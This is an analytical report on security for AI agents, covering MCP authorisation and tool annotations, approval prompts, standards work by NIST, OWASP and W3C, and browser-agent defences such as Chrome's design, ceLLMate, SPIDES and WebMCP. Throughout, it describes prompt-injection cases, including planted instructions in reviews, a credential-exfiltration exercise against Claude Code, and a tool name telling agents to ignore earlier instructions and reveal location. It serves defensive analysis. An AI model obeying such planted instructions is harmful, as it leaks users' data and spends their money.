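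Standing rules also reduce prompts, but they did worse in Yan's experiment. One group chose "allow", "ask" or "never" in advance for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, which left most decisions for later. This group saw about 11 prompts instead of 18, but stopped about 40% of the actions that went beyond the task, compared with 59.6% for people who approved every action.

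Fatigue alone can't explain this result, because the group with fewer prompts approved more of the unwanted actions it saw. Writing the rules may have made people feel that they had already dealt with the risk. The comparison is imperfect because Yan assigned all the later recruits to the rules group. Still, the result is a reason not to assume that people will decide better if a product asks them less often.

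### What a person can add

In *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025), people supervising an agent were less likely to fall for manipulative website designs in 14 of 16 tasks. They often stopped the agent when it did something unexpected, such as skipping the terms and conditions. But they focused on the path the agent had chosen and noticed less of the rest of the page.

Experienced users of Claude Code seem to supervise in a similar way. They approve more actions automatically but also interrupt the agent more often. Anthropic warns that this kind of supervision depends on the user noticing when the agent goes off course, which becomes harder as commands grow more complex and several agents run at once.

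Users can also unknowingly give an agent harmful instructions. In a February 2026 exercise, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that included an instruction to send out secret credentials. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 repetitions. An approval prompt might not have helped, because the employee believed the task was legitimate. Anthropic concluded that only limits on file and network access would have reliably kept the credentials from being sent.

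Automatic reviewers can also misjudge what a user has agreed to. In March 2026, auto mode's classifier missed 17% of 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond what the user wanted. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as approved by the user. For example, it treated one user's request to "clean up the PR", a set of proposed code changes, as permission to overwrite the project's history. In a case like this, asking the user would settle what the request meant, provided the prompt made clear that the history would be lost. Anthropic accepts that auto mode may be worse than manual review for someone who checks every action carefully, and it still recommends human review for high-stakes changes.

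## What have agent protocols and public standards programmes agreed so far?

Agent protocols and standards bodies have agreed mainly on how an agent identifies itself and gets access to an account. They recommend human approval but leave the details to each product, and they have agreed on few limits on what an agent can do once it has access. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has gone furthest.

### How MCP added authorisation

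Anthropic launched the Model Context Protocol (MCP) in November 2024. *Two Years of MCP Builders* (Soria Parra and Delimarsky, 2026) reports that more than 2,500 people have contributed since. The first version had no standard way for a server to check whether an agent was allowed to use someone's account. The March 2025 version added one based on OAuth, an older web standard that lets people give a program access to an account without sharing their password.

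If the airline in the flight example runs an MCP server, the process in Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) works like this:

1. The agent's client calls the airline's server without credentials. The server refuses, and its reply can name the permission the client needs, such as `flights:read`.
2. The client finds the airline's sign-in service and opens it in the employee's browser.
3. The employee signs in and approves the access.
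4. The sign-in service sends back a code, which the client exchanges for an access token.
5. The client attaches the token to every later request, and the airline's server checks it.

Later versions closed gaps in this process. Suppose the agent also uses an attacker's hotel server. If the client gave that server a token that worked at the airline, the attacker could use the employee's airline account. Since June 2025, Model Context Protocol (2025) has required clients to name the intended server when they request a token. Servers must reject tokens issued for any other server.

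The November 2025 version let an agent collect permissions as it needs them. The agent can start with permission to search, and if it only searches, it never gets permission to buy. If it calls `book_flight`, the server rejects the call and specifies the missing permission, and the client asks the employee to grant it.

The newest version, from July 2026, addresses an attack on clients that use several sign-in services. A malicious service could trick the client into sending it a code issued by the airline's service. The client must now record which service it expects a reply from and check the name in the reply before redeeming the code. But the specification only recommends ("SHOULD") that sign-in services include their name. If a service neither includes its name nor advertises that it does, the client proceeds without the check. The maintainers expect to make the name mandatory in a future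 version. *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (Delimarsky and Soria Parra, 2026) gives 30 March 2027 as the date of the next version.

### Strict rules in an optional system

*The Anatomy of MCP Authorization* (Dissanayaka, 2026) describes the July changes as non-negotiable requirements, and SC Media's *Model Context Protocol overhaul introduces new security challenges for developers* (2026) reported that the new version mandates OAuth 2.1. Both descriptions are accurate only for servers and clients that use the authorisation system, which is still OPTIONAL. Even for web-based servers that support authorisation, following these rules is only a SHOULD, which allows exceptions.

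Tools that communicate with the client directly on the user's computer SHOULD NOT use this system. They take their credentials from that computer's settings instead. A coding agent's local tools may therefore have all the access those credentials provide, without the user seeing a sign-in page.

The documents behind these rules also vary in status. MCP is the specification of an open-source project, now under the Agentic AI Foundation, and the OAuth 2.1 text it relies on is an IETF Internet-Draft. MCP is widely used despite this. Model Context Protocol's *The 2026-07-28 Specification* (2026) reports nearly half a billion downloads a month across its main software kits, though one developer can account for many downloads.

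New versions can also create new weaknesses. Clients must now repeat the tool's name in a header, so that a company's gateway can check it without opening the message. SC Media reports a warning from Akamai, an internet infrastructure company, that the header and the message might not match. An attacker could put `search_flights` in the header and `book_flight` in the message, and a gateway that reads only the header would let the purchase through. The specification has an error code for this mismatch, but that helps only if some software compares the two.

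A more basic limit is that authorisation also doesn't establish whether the agent is doing what the employee asked. A token can show that the employee allowed this client to book flights, but a general booking permission also covers a flight on the wrong date. The token remains valid even if the agent has followed instructions planted in a hotel review.

### One tool call and its annotations

Before an agent can call the airline's booking tool, its client gets a description of the tool from the server. The description might look like this:

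```json
{
  "name": "book_flight",
  "description": "Buy a ticket for the chosen flight",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": { "flight_id": { "type": "string" } },
    "required": ["flight_id"]
  },
  "annotations": {
    "readOnlyHint": false,
    "destructiveHint": false,
    "idempotentHint": false,
    "openWorldHint": true
  }
}
```

When the model decides to book, the client sends a call. Leaving out some routine metadata, it looks like this:

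```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "book_flight",
    "arguments": { "flight_id": "NYC-0815" }
  }
}
```

The annotations are in the tool's description, not in the call, so the client has to act on them before it sends anything. `readOnlyHint: false` is a reason to ask the employee first. `idempotentHint: false` means repeating the call may have a further effect, so a client that retries after a lost connection could buy two tickets. `openWorldHint: true` means the tool deals with outside parties, so its results may contain untrusted text.

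The value of `destructiveHint` is less obvious. The protocol's maintainers advise developers to set it to false for tools that only add something. Buying a ticket adds a booking and deletes nothing, and none of the four annotations covers spending money, so an honest airline could reasonably choose false. A client that warned people only about destructive tools would then let the agent spend several hundred dollars without a warning.

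### Why clients must not trust the annotations

People involved in the Model Context Protocol (MCP) disagreed about annotations from the start. According to MCP's March 2026 post, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked how a client could use an annotation it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers. The compromise was to call every annotation a hint, require clients to distrust hints by default, and let each client decide how much weight to give them.

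This works reasonably well for a company that runs its own servers, because it knows who wrote the labels, but less well for someone who installs a server found online. Most clients trust any server that has been installed, according to the same post, so a server's author can gain that trust by persuading someone to install it.

Accurately labelled tools can still be dangerous in combination. The developer Simon Willison calls it the "lethal trifecta" when an agent can read private data, encounters untrusted content and can send information out. On the travel site, one tool might read the employee's passport number, another might fetch hotel reviews and a third might submit forms. Together, they could let an attacker who plants instructions in a review steal the passport number, even if each tool's annotations are accurate. Because people mix tools from several servers, no server's developer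 can see the whole combination.

By March 2026, contributors had proposed five additions to address such gaps. GitHub and OpenAI staff wrote one, on marking sensitive and untrusted data, after running into the problem in their own products. With these labels, a client could detect that a session had read untrusted text and apply stricter rules to anything that sends data out. The list of changes for the July version in Model Context Protocol (2026) includes no new behaviour annotations.

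Clients didn't make much use of the limited information in the protocol's existing annotations either. In March, no MCP client showed annotations in its approval prompts or let people filter tools by them.

### Human approval is only a recommendation

The Model Context Protocol's page on tools recommends that a person always be able to refuse a tool call. Clients SHOULD also log tool calls and show the user a tool's inputs before sending them, which could let the user notice a passport number about to go to the wrong server. But the protocol doesn't require any particular way of involving the user, so even Claude Code's auto mode can conform.

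A stricter rule might not have helped much. If MCP required a prompt before every call, clients would probably show so many prompts that people would approve them without reading them.

Since June 2025, MCP has also let a server ask the user for information partway through a task. As of the July 2026 version, the server no longer has to hold a connection open while it waits for the answer. When the agent calls `book_flight`, the airline's server can reply with a question such as "Buy this ticket for $640?" The client gets an answer and sends the call again with it attached. Supabase, a database company, plans to use this to confirm a new project's cost or a query that would delete data.

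This lets the party that knows the price decide when to ask. However, the answer still arrives through the agent's client, and nothing in the message format proves that a person gave it, so a carelessly built client could let the model answer instead.

### Agents that deal with other agents and with websites

MCP connects an agent to tools. Agent2Agent (A2A) lets agents from different companies pass tasks to each other. For example, the employee's travel agent could ask a hotel chain's agent to find a room. Google introduced A2A in April 2025 and later gave it to the Linux Foundation.

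An agent that accepts tasks through the Agent2Agent (A2A) protocol publishes an Agent Card, a file that lists its skills, address and supported sign-in methods. The owner can sign the card so that others can detect changes. A task can pause until the requesting side supplies more information or credentials. Like the Model Context Protocol (MCP), A2A is an open-source project's specification and lets the receiving side decide what to permit. When an employee's travel agent contacts a hotel's agent, the hotel's agent can verify who is asking, but it has to rely on the travel agent for what the employee wanted.

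Websites also need to know who operates an agent that arrives through a browser. The IETF's Web Bot Auth work lets the operator sign the agent's web requests and publish a public key, which websites use to check that the requests came from that operator. A browser label such as "ChatGPT" doesn't prove this, since any program can send the same label. The signature method is an IETF Proposed Standard. The IETF formed a working group in 2025 to apply it to bots and agents, starting from Internet-Drafts, which have no formal status.

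In *Know Your Agent*, a briefing for public services and businesses, Loosemore (2026) notes that some cloud-based agents now sign their traffic, while others act inside the customer's own browser and may look like an ordinary logged-in user to a service such as an airline. Loosemore recommends that services check any evidence an agent provides and also limit the action itself, for example with a spending cap or a fresh confirmation. These limits still apply if the agent sends no signature, or if an attacker has hijacked an agent whose signature is valid.

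### A shared list of risks

OWASP, a non-profit organisation best known for its lists of web security flaws, published a *Top 10 for Agentic Applications* in December 2025. The first entry is "agent goal hijack", in which an attacker changes what the agent is trying to do, as the planted review does. Other entries include tool misuse, abuse of the agent's identity and privileges, unexpected code execution, and poisoned memory.

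OWASP's list gives developers and buyers a common vocabulary. A company can ask a supplier how its agent handles each risk, even if the supplier uses different names for its safeguards. But the list is only guidance, so one supplier can claim to address tool misuse with a sandbox and another with a sentence in the model's instructions.

OWASP has since moved towards controls. Mittelstand Cafe's *Der KI-Agent erledigt seinen Auftrag. Genau das kann zum Problem werden* (2026), a German press release, describes a new OWASP Agent Control Standard for controlling agents while they work. Developers choose whether to adopt it.

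### NIST's initiative

The United States government began by requesting information on how developers secure agents and measure that security. NIST's Center for AI Standards and Innovation, formerly the US AI Safety Institute, issued the request in January 2026. ANSI's *Mitigating Risks of AI Agent Systems* (2026) gives 9 March as the deadline for replies.

The centre launched the AI Agent Standards Initiative on 17 February. ANSI's *NIST Launches AI Agent Standards Initiative* (2026) lists its three strands:

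- helping industry develop agent standards and promoting US leadership in international standards bodies
- supporting open-source protocols for agents
- funding and carrying out research on agent security and identity.

NIST also published a concept paper on how organisations could use existing identity standards to recognise agents and control their access. Comments were due by 2 April, according to the law firm Pillsbury. NIST separately invited submissions, due by 20 March, for listening sessions on what prevents organisations, including banks, from adopting AI.

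These documents collected views and set no requirements. Digital Policy Alert, which tracks regulation, lists the initiative's status at its February launch as "under deliberation". NIST made identity the subject of both a research strand and the concept paper, so it started in the area where MCP had made the most progress.

Voluntary guidance from NIST can also gain some force later. Pillsbury advises financial institutions to take part early because practical standards may influence procurement rules and supervisors' decisions. A bank or federal agency might then refuse to buy an agent from a developer that ignores a NIST guideline.

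### What W3C's strategy team proposes

W3C's strategy paper of 20 October 2026 is a discussion document by W3C staff, not a standard. Le Hegaret argues that prompt injection and misbehaving agents undermine the same-origin protections the web depends on. The paper also warns that agents carry data between contexts and that people may not meaningfully consent to what an agent does.

MCP alone can't fill these gaps. Le Hegaret doubts that companies will ever offer as many MCP servers as there are websites, so agents would still reach most sites through the browser.

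According to KIberblick's German summary, *W3C will Regeln für KI-Agenten im Web* (2026), the proposed actions include having W3C's Security Interest Group write threat models for agents, WebMCP and AI features built into browsers. A threat model lists who might attack a system and how, and is ideally written before the safeguards. Another aim is for agents to prove that they act for a person without knowing that person's passwords.

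The privacy proposals cover information that an agent keeps after a task. Reviews would examine its memory, the data it moves between sites, and its logs of prompts and tool calls. One proposal is an incognito mode in which the agent remembers nothing. An agent that used an employee's passport number to book a flight in this mode couldn't reveal the number on an unrelated site a month later.

The paper also calls for real consent before consequential actions and warns about approval fatigue. It recommends ways to see what an agent did, undo it where possible and withdraw the agent's authority. For payments, it proposes spending limits, receipts and a way to complain. MCP's annotations and tokens provide few of these safeguards.

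Agents don't yet buy much. According to figures Le Hegaret cites from HUMAN Security, a bot-detection company, only 2.3% of agent visits in June 2026 reached checkout or payment pages. KIberblick considers this a good time to write rules, before agents place a large share of orders. There may not be much time, because agent traffic is growing quickly. Le Hegaret also cites Cloudflare, whose network received over 18 times as many daily agent requests in September 2026 as a year earlier.

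W3C doesn't yet have a group to turn all this into standards. Its Web & AI Interest Group is chartered to publish reports but not Recommendations (W3C, 2025), so the strategy paper proposes an Agentic Web Working Group. *Reflections from TPAC 2026* (de Vries, 2026), an account of W3C's annual meeting in October, reports broad consensus to form one. The members would still have to agree on its scope and then on its documents, and KIberblick expects standards to take years.

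W3C's Technical Architecture Group reviews proposals for their effect on the web as a whole. Its *User Agents* (Yasskin and Capadisli, 2026) lists duties of protection, honesty and loyalty that browsers and other software acting on web content owe the people they act for. The document is a Group Note, which neither W3C nor its members endorse. Developers also can't work out from a duty of loyalty when their software should stop a purchase.

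### Which safeguards are now shared?

| Safeguard | What exists across products | What each product still decides |
|---|---|---|
| Access to accounts | OAuth rules in MCP; sign-in methods in A2A | Whether to require authorisation, and how broad each permission is |
| Identifying agents to websites | Signed requests, through the IETF's work | Whether to sign, and how to treat unsigned visitors |
| Describing a tool's risks | Four MCP annotations | Whether to supply them, trust them or show them to users |
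| Human approval | MCP's advice and its format for questions during a call | When to ask, what to show, and whether a classifier can answer instead |
| Resistance to prompt injection | OWASP's description of the risk | Training, classifiers and separation of untrusted text |
| Sandboxes | A recommendation from MCP's maintainers for cases that need a guarantee | Which files and servers the agent can reach |
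| Spending limits and undo | Proposals from W3C's strategy team | Nearly everything |

Commercial need probably explains much of this pattern. An agent and an airline can't connect securely unless both use the same sign-in process, so companies have to agree on one before they can do business. According to the July release post, developers spend most of their integration time on authorisation. A sandbox works without anyone else's agreement, so its maker has less reason to negotiate a common design.

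Authorisation is also easier to enforce from outside the client. If a client sends a token meant for another server, the airline's server can reject it, and the client's developer soon discovers the mistake. If the client trusts a false annotation or skips an approval prompt, the booking still goes through and the airline may never know.

Progress on identity also has an important gap. *The New MCP Roadmap* (Soria Parra and Delimarsky, 2026) acknowledges that MCP's authorisation assumes a person is approving access in a browser. But more and more agents run in the cloud while their user is away, or hand part of a task to helper agents that should have narrower powers. The maintainers plan a standard way to recognise these agents and pass on limited authority. They also want to finish a method that ties a token to a secret key, so that a stolen token is useless without the key. Until then,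 developers often have to use copied access keys and long-lived tokens, which give a helper agent the same powers as the agent that started it.

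## What can a browser enforce on an agent?

A browser can limit which sites an agent reads and acts on, block individual requests, and hold an action until the user confirms it. These checks don't cover agents that work outside the browser, and it usually takes a model to decide what a task requires.

### Why the same-origin policy doesn't contain an agent

An agent can carry a passport number from one site to another without breaking the same-origin policy, because it acts with the user's access and doesn't need a script. *Privacy and security considerations for WebMCP* (Huang, 2025) assumes that agents can inherit the user's identity from the browser, see context from several sites, and hold payment details.

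Boundaries within a page can disappear too. A browser keeps an advertisement's frame separate from the shop around it, but many agents work from a text version of the page. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (2026) points out that in that version, the advertisement and the shop's checkout button are both just text.

Wang and colleagues measured how easily an attacker can exploit this. An agent handled private information on one test site, then visited a second page with a planted instruction to reveal it. ChatGPT Atlas, running GPT-5.5, revealed the information in 99 of 150 runs, though newer models may resist better. Without the planted instructions, agents that visited the two pages in turn leaked nothing.

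The proposed remedy, SOPGuard, labels each piece of data with its origin and asks the user before the agent writes it to another origin. In BrowserOS, an open-source browser, it eliminated violations and increased running time by 2% to 6%. But many ordinary tasks involve moving data between sites, so users would see many prompts, and people tend to stop reading prompts that appear often.

Data can also leak without leaving its origin. A planted instruction could make an agent post someone's account details in a public review on the same shop's site, and SOPGuard would allow it. *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) concludes that restoring the same-origin policy is neither necessary nor sufficient to protect users.

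### Three conditions for an attack

W3C's *Agentic Browsing and the Web's Security Model* (2025), the draft minutes of a November session, records a discussion of a threat model with three conditions. The agent reads untrusted content, has access to private data or other capabilities, and can change something, for example by placing an order. This is broader than Willison's "lethal trifecta", which requires the agent to send information out. One participant noted that an attacker who makes an agent change a router's settings doesn't need to see any data.

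Removing any one of the three conditions would prevent the attack, but a shopping agent needs them all because it reads reviews, uses the customer's account and places the order. One participant therefore suggested an "outer envelope" of fixed rules, such as which sites the agent may act on and where it may fill in passwords or card numbers. Model-based defences might then be good enough for many of the actions those rules still allow, which form the "inner envelope".

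Another participant asked what would stop a shop from using prompt injection to sell a slightly more expensive product within the user's price limit. Fixed rules wouldn't stop this, and a trick that fools one copy of an agent could work against every customer who uses that agent. Someone replied that an overpriced sweater is less frightening than a shop that can read your email. That priority seems sensible, but shops could still manipulate agents into overpaying.

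W3C listed the session's goals as brainstorming and sharing knowledge, so the threat model is not an agreed standard.

### A shopping task in Chrome

Suppose an employee asks Chrome's agent to find a well-reviewed suitcase for under $150 and buy it. A review on a comparison site contains a planted instruction to open the employee's webmail and send the latest message to an attacker. Under the design that Parker described in December 2025, the task would go like this:

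1. The planner, the main Gemini model, proposes the sites it needs. A gating function that never sees web content judges whether they are relevant. The comparison site goes into the read-only set, and the shop into the set where the agent may also click and type.
2. The agent opens the comparison site. By a fixed rule, Chrome hides any frame whose origin isn't in the sets, so the planner doesn't see an unrelated advertisement. It does see the planted review, which is part of the comparison site's own page.
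3. A classifier scans the page for prompt injection while the planner works, and can block actions that result from it. This is a model judgement, and Parker accepts that the classifier will miss some attacks.
4. If it misses this one, the planner may try to open the webmail site. Another model judges whether the new site is relevant to buying a suitcase, and should refuse. A fixed rule also limits addresses written by the planner to known, public ones, so it can't smuggle private text out inside a web address.
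5. The planner proposes adding a suitcase to the cart. A separate model, the User Alignment Critic, receives a description of the action but none of the page's untrusted content. It judges whether the action serves the employee's goal. If it rejects the action, the planner tries another plan, and after repeated failures it can return control to the employee.
6. The shop asks the agent to sign in. Chrome gets the employee's confirmation before using a password saved in Google Password Manager, and the planner has no direct access to the password. This appears to be a fixed rule. A fixed list of sensitive sites, such as banks, triggers a similar confirmation before the agent opens one.
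7. At the payment page, the agent tries to pause and either asks permission or has the employee finish the purchase. Recognising that a step needs this pause depends at least partly on a model.

The critic uses CaMeL's idea of keeping untrusted text away from a trusted model, but Chrome's planner still reads the page. A planted review can't influence the critic's approval through its text, but it can lead the agent to choose a poor $140 suitcase. The critic presumably can't detect this, since the employee asked for a suitcase.

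The payment check isn't simply a fixed rule, which is a little worrying because a mistake there can cost the most. Google runs automated attacks against the system and offers up to $20,000 to researchers who breach it. Parker doesn't say how often those attacks succeed, so outsiders can't judge how well the layers work together.

### What has changed since launch

Google launched the agent, called auto browse, on 28 January 2026, according to Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026). In July, Google connected it to Gemini Spark, an agent that works in the background. With the user's permission, Spark can use logged-in accounts and saved passwords in Chrome, but Google's *Gemini Spark now integrates with Chrome* says it will hand control back to the user for payments. PPC Land reported that the feature wasn't available in the European Economic Area,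 the UK, Switzerland or Nigeria.

Auto browse reached paying Android users in the United States in August. *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?* (Kanchwala, 2026) reports that paying users in India got it in October. Google says it asks for confirmation before "some sensitive tasks". Android Central's *Gemini's auto-browse in Chrome is finally here for Android* reports that the phone version also shows users its plan for review. This may be useful, since Claude Code's users rejected plans much more often than individual actions.

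*Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) describes new controls for companies. A company can apply the same data-loss rules to an agent as to its employees, and Chrome's history marks the background pages an agent opened. The post repeats the plan to confine agents to relevant origins, but doesn't say whether Chrome now tracks the read-only set, which Google left out of its first version. Google has expanded what the agent can reach since launch, but its public description of the origin limits has hardly changed.

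### ceLLMate checks requests instead of clicks

Chrome's origin sets can't distinguish between reading an order and cancelling it on the same site. *CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) describes ceLLMate, a research sandbox that can. The sandbox is a Chrome extension that works with any agent using the browser.

ceLLMate checks the requests a browser sends to a website's server. An agent normally can't buy or delete anything without such a request, and its meaning is much clearer than a click's. A rule about clicks would be nearly useless, because the same spot on the screen might open an email on one page and delete it on another. Agents also find other routes to a blocked site. When the researchers stopped an agent from going directly to a site, it found the site through a search engine and clicked the result.

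For "buy a coffee maker on Amazon for under $50", it would work like this:

1. Amazon publishes an agent sitemap, a file that matches requests to named actions. A request to the checkout's `place-order` address, for example, means `PlaceOrder`.
2. Amazon or another trusted party writes policies for those actions, such as one that allows `PlaceOrder` only up to a chosen amount.
3. A model reads the user's request and the available policies, but no product pages. It selects the smallest set of policies that will do the job and fills in the $50 limit. The user checks the selection and can change it.
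4. The extension compares each request with the policies. It takes the total from the checkout page and blocks the order if the total is over $50.

After the user confirms the policies, nothing the agent reads can change them. An optional counter stops the agent from getting around the spending limit by placing two $49 orders. ceLLMate rejects requests that don't name a site, such as "buy a coffee maker", because the site determines which policies apply.

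The researchers tested the ceLLMate sandbox on GitLab, a site for managing code, with policies that let an agent read and write issues. They wrote 12 scripts that behaved like a completely hijacked agent, with goals such as deleting projects or creating access tokens. The sandbox blocked all 12.

Each of those attacks needed an action that the policy didn't allow. An agent with permission to comment could still post a stolen password in a comment, because ceLLMate doesn't track where the text came from. The perfect score is good evidence that the blocking works, but not that an attack using only allowed actions would fail.

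ceLLMate's protection adds little overhead. A test of 11 page visits took 13.93 seconds without it, 14.94 seconds (7.25% longer) with a sitemap of 100 entries, and 16.02 seconds (15% longer) with 300. Users would probably not notice the delay, since an agent's model usually takes longer than the browser. The extension used about 25 MB of memory.

Choosing the policies is less reliable than enforcing them. Three models from 2025 picked exactly the right policies for at least 94% of tasks in each category of website. On shopping tasks that also needed a value, such as a price limit, they got both the policies and the values right 81% to 97% of the time. The user has to notice the remaining mistakes in the confirmation dialog.

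### Who would write the rules?

Meng and colleagues expect website developers to write the sitemaps, and compare this work to documenting an API. Policies could come from the same developers, a company's administrators or independent maintainers like those of the EasyList filters for ad blockers.

The researchers cite Content Security Policy (CSP) as evidence that developers will maintain a file like the sitemap. CSP's history is not very encouraging, because most sites' script policies did little to stop cross-site scripting, the attack they were meant to prevent. A sitemap may be easier to get right, since it describes the site's own requests, while a script policy also depends on other companies' code. Writing one still takes work, as the researchers wrote 51 entries for GitLab by hand, and any action missing from the sitemap is no safer than before.

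*Permission Manifests for Web Agents* (2026) proposes a less demanding option for sites, a file called `agent-permissions.json` that lists what agents may do. The proposal deliberately leaves out enforcement, partly because small sites may not be able to afford it. That could help more sites adopt the file, but the file by itself can't make agents comply.

SPIDES requires more detail from websites, which label parts of each page as trusted or untrusted and list who may see private parts. The software that drives the browser replaces untrusted text, such as a review, with a placeholder. If the agent chooses to read the original, it then needs the user's approval for any action with consequences on a trusted site. This lets SPIDES catch leaks within one site that SOPGuard misses.

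Zverev and colleagues tested SPIDES on 28 linked test websites. They assumed that an attacker could choose a model's output whenever the model read untrusted text. SPIDES blocked every attack, while 53% to 73% succeeded against SOPGuard, depending on the model. Agents using SPIDES completed 67% to 86% of the legitimate tasks.

These results depend on correct labels. On a site the user trusts, SPIDES treats anything without a label as trusted and public, so a developer who forgets to label the reviews leaves the agent exposed. CSP 1.0 had a similar weakness, since browsers allowed whatever a policy didn't mention. Some sites may also have reasons to label content dishonestly. At the W3C session, one participant said that a publisher that didn't want agents reading its site would want to mark its articles as untrusted and its advertisements as trusted.

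### How other browsers differ

Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested browser agents in January and February 2026 and found little consistency:

| Agent | Reads frames from other origins | Reads tabs from other origins | Types on a page when the user asks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | With permission | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas, agent mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes, in auto browse |
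| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |

Some limits on browser agents are part of the software. When the user clicked "Summarize page", Firefox gave its agent only the text of the outer page, so an instruction hidden in a frame couldn't reach it. Others seem to depend on the model declining to act. For example, Claude for Chrome refused to follow instructions on a page, but it could run its own code on any site it had access to. Anthropic blocks it from some sensitive sites, such as banks.

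The most restrictive products were the least useful as agents, because they couldn't fill in forms. These tests are from early 2026, and the products may have changed since. At the time, Roesner and Kohlbrenner recommended that people avoid agentic browsers altogether.

### Agents outside the browser

Chrome's origin sets don't apply when an agent works without a browser, such as when a coding agent contacts a website with a command like `curl` or an agent books a flight through an airline's MCP server. In these cases, the operating system or the website has to stop a bad action. Other agents use browsers with few protections. At the W3C session, a participant who works on MCP described tools that ask people to put their master password in a configuration file for the agent.

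Malicious extensions could also manipulate the agents in Chrome, Edge, Comet and Opera Neon, as well as Claude in Chrome, according to *BragJack Shows How Malicious Extensions Can Hijack AI Browser Agents* (Ofonagoro, 2026). ceLLMate is itself an extension and assumes that no other extension is tampering with its requests. Building it into the browser would remove the need for that assumption, but would require the browser maker's cooperation.

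So far, each vendor has its own design, so a shop can't write one set of rules that Chrome, Atlas and Comet will all enforce. The research systems use still other formats. W3C's Threat Modeling Community Group has begun an open list of threats to agentic browsers. In *Threat Modeling Agentic AI Web Browsers*, Onofri (2025) invited others to help write it. The list could give vendors a shared description of the threats, but they would still need a shared way to block them.

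One participant in the W3C session proposed treating the browser and the agent as separate, so that the browser could enforce fixed rules on any agent. This enforcement would be easiest to check if different companies made the browser and the agent, but Chrome and Atlas are each made by the same company as their agent.

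## What does the WebMCP dispute show about standardising before the safety model is settled?

WebMCP is probably the closest thing to a shared browser design for agents. It went from a proposal to live products in about a year, while its W3C reviewers still disagreed about its risks. Its developers argue that other software has to deal with the worst of those risks, and they are largely right. But WebMCP also creates some risks of its own, and most of its protections against them are only advice to the agent.

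### How a page offers a tool

A travel site can offer its booking function to agents in two ways. Its developer can add labels to an ordinary HTML form, using WebMCP's declarative API, or register a JavaScript function through the imperative API. The second might look like this:

```js
await document.modelContext.registerTool({
  name: 'book_flight',
  description: 'Buy a ticket for the chosen flight',
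  inputSchema: {
    type: 'object',
    properties: { flight_id: { type: 'string' } },
    required: ['flight_id']
  },
  annotations: { consequentialHint: true },
  execute: async ({ flight_id }) => bookFlight(flight_id)
}, {
  exposedTo: ['https://partner.example']
});
```

The unofficial guide webmcp.org describes four steps:

1. The page registers the tool with the browser.
2. The agent asks the browser which tools the page offers and what input each one needs.
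3. The agent chooses `book_flight` and supplies the flight's identifier.
4. The browser runs the page's own function inside the page, with the employee's existing login.

The page can also remove a tool or add one later, so `book_flight` need not exist until the employee has picked a flight.

WebMCP takes its tool format from MCP but doesn't use MCP's protocol, and the airline doesn't need to run an MCP server. A tool call does need an open tab or a similar window, according to The Drop Times' *Google Details WebMCP Origin Trial for Chrome 149 With DevTools Support*. An open window doesn't guarantee that anyone is watching, because other software can drive the browser and WebMCP can't check whether a person is there.

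### What the browser enforces

| Provision | Purpose | Who has to act on it |
|---|---|---|
| Origin limits, including `exposedTo` | Hide a tool from other origins unless the page lists them | The browser enforces them |
| `tools` Permissions Policy | Controls which frames may use WebMCP | The browser enforces it |
| `untrustedContentHint` | Warns that a tool's output may contain outsiders' text | The agent decides how to treat the text |
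| `consequentialHint` | Marks a purchase or another serious action | The agent or browser may ask for confirmation |
| `readOnlyHint` | Marks a tool that changes nothing | The agent may skip confirmation |
| `requestUserInteraction()` | Lets a tool ask the user something while it runs | The site has to call it and wait for the answer |

The origin limits protect sites from one another. In the example, the partner site can use `book_flight` when one site embeds the other, but an advertiser's frame can't see it. Chrome for Developers (2026) warns in its security guidance that sharing even a read-only tool can be risky, because a tool such as `getFavoriteProducts` reveals information about the user. The limits don't restrict where an agent takes the information it gets from a tool.

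The hints resemble MCP's annotations, but `consequentialHint` adds a label for bookings and payments. If an airline labelled its payment step honestly, Chrome could always ask the user before running the tool, instead of relying partly on a model to recognise the step. Google's guidance permits the agent or browser to ask but doesn't require it.

A dishonest site can leave the label off or put an attack in the tool's description. One of Huang's slides from November 2025 shows a weather tool whose name contains an order to ignore earlier instructions and reveal the user's location. The agent has to read names and descriptions to choose a tool, so this attack can work before the agent calls any tool.

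A site can't force agents to use its tools either. *AI agents and the web* (2025), an early introduction for developers, notes that an agent can still read and operate the page without them. If `book_flight` pauses for the employee's consent, an agent might press the ordinary booking button instead, so the airline would need the same check on that button.

### From explainer to live products

Six people from Microsoft and Google published the first WebMCP explainer on 13 August 2025, according to a Korean introduction, *WebMCP, Web 문서를 읽는 AI 에이전트에게 사용 가능한 기능을 도구로 알려주는 웹* (2026). W3C's Technical Architecture Group (TAG) discussed the proposal with the Community Group that November. Minutes from W3C (2025) record that the TAG's "loudest concern" then was that MCP wouldn't last.

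Google offered an early preview of WebMCP in Chrome 146 in February 2026, which developers had to switch on. On a W3C mailing list, Di Maio pointed out that the accessibility section of the 27 February draft was empty, and that the security and privacy section held only a to-do note linking to another document. Jones (2026) warned W3C's security group of a "privacy / security nightmare" and asked how to bring the proposal to the right people's attention.

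The empty section made the work look more careless than it was, because Huang had already listed several kinds of attack in a separate document, which a colleague called "pretty solid". But a list of attacks doesn't settle who has to stop each one. Minutes from W3C (2026) show that the Community Group still had no draft threat model on 14 May, when it resolved to ask the TAG and the security and privacy groups for early reviews.

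InfoQ's *WebMCP Standard Proposal for Agentic Web Actuation Now Available in Chrome* (2026) reported in June that WebMCP was entering an origin trial, a test with real users, in Chrome 149. By August, Edge 150 had one too. On 11 June, the team behind WebKit, the engine in Apple's Safari, formally opposed the proposal. The TAG review opened the same day. Dominic Farolino, who leads work on the specification at Google, complained that someone had requested the review before WebMCP's developers were ready.

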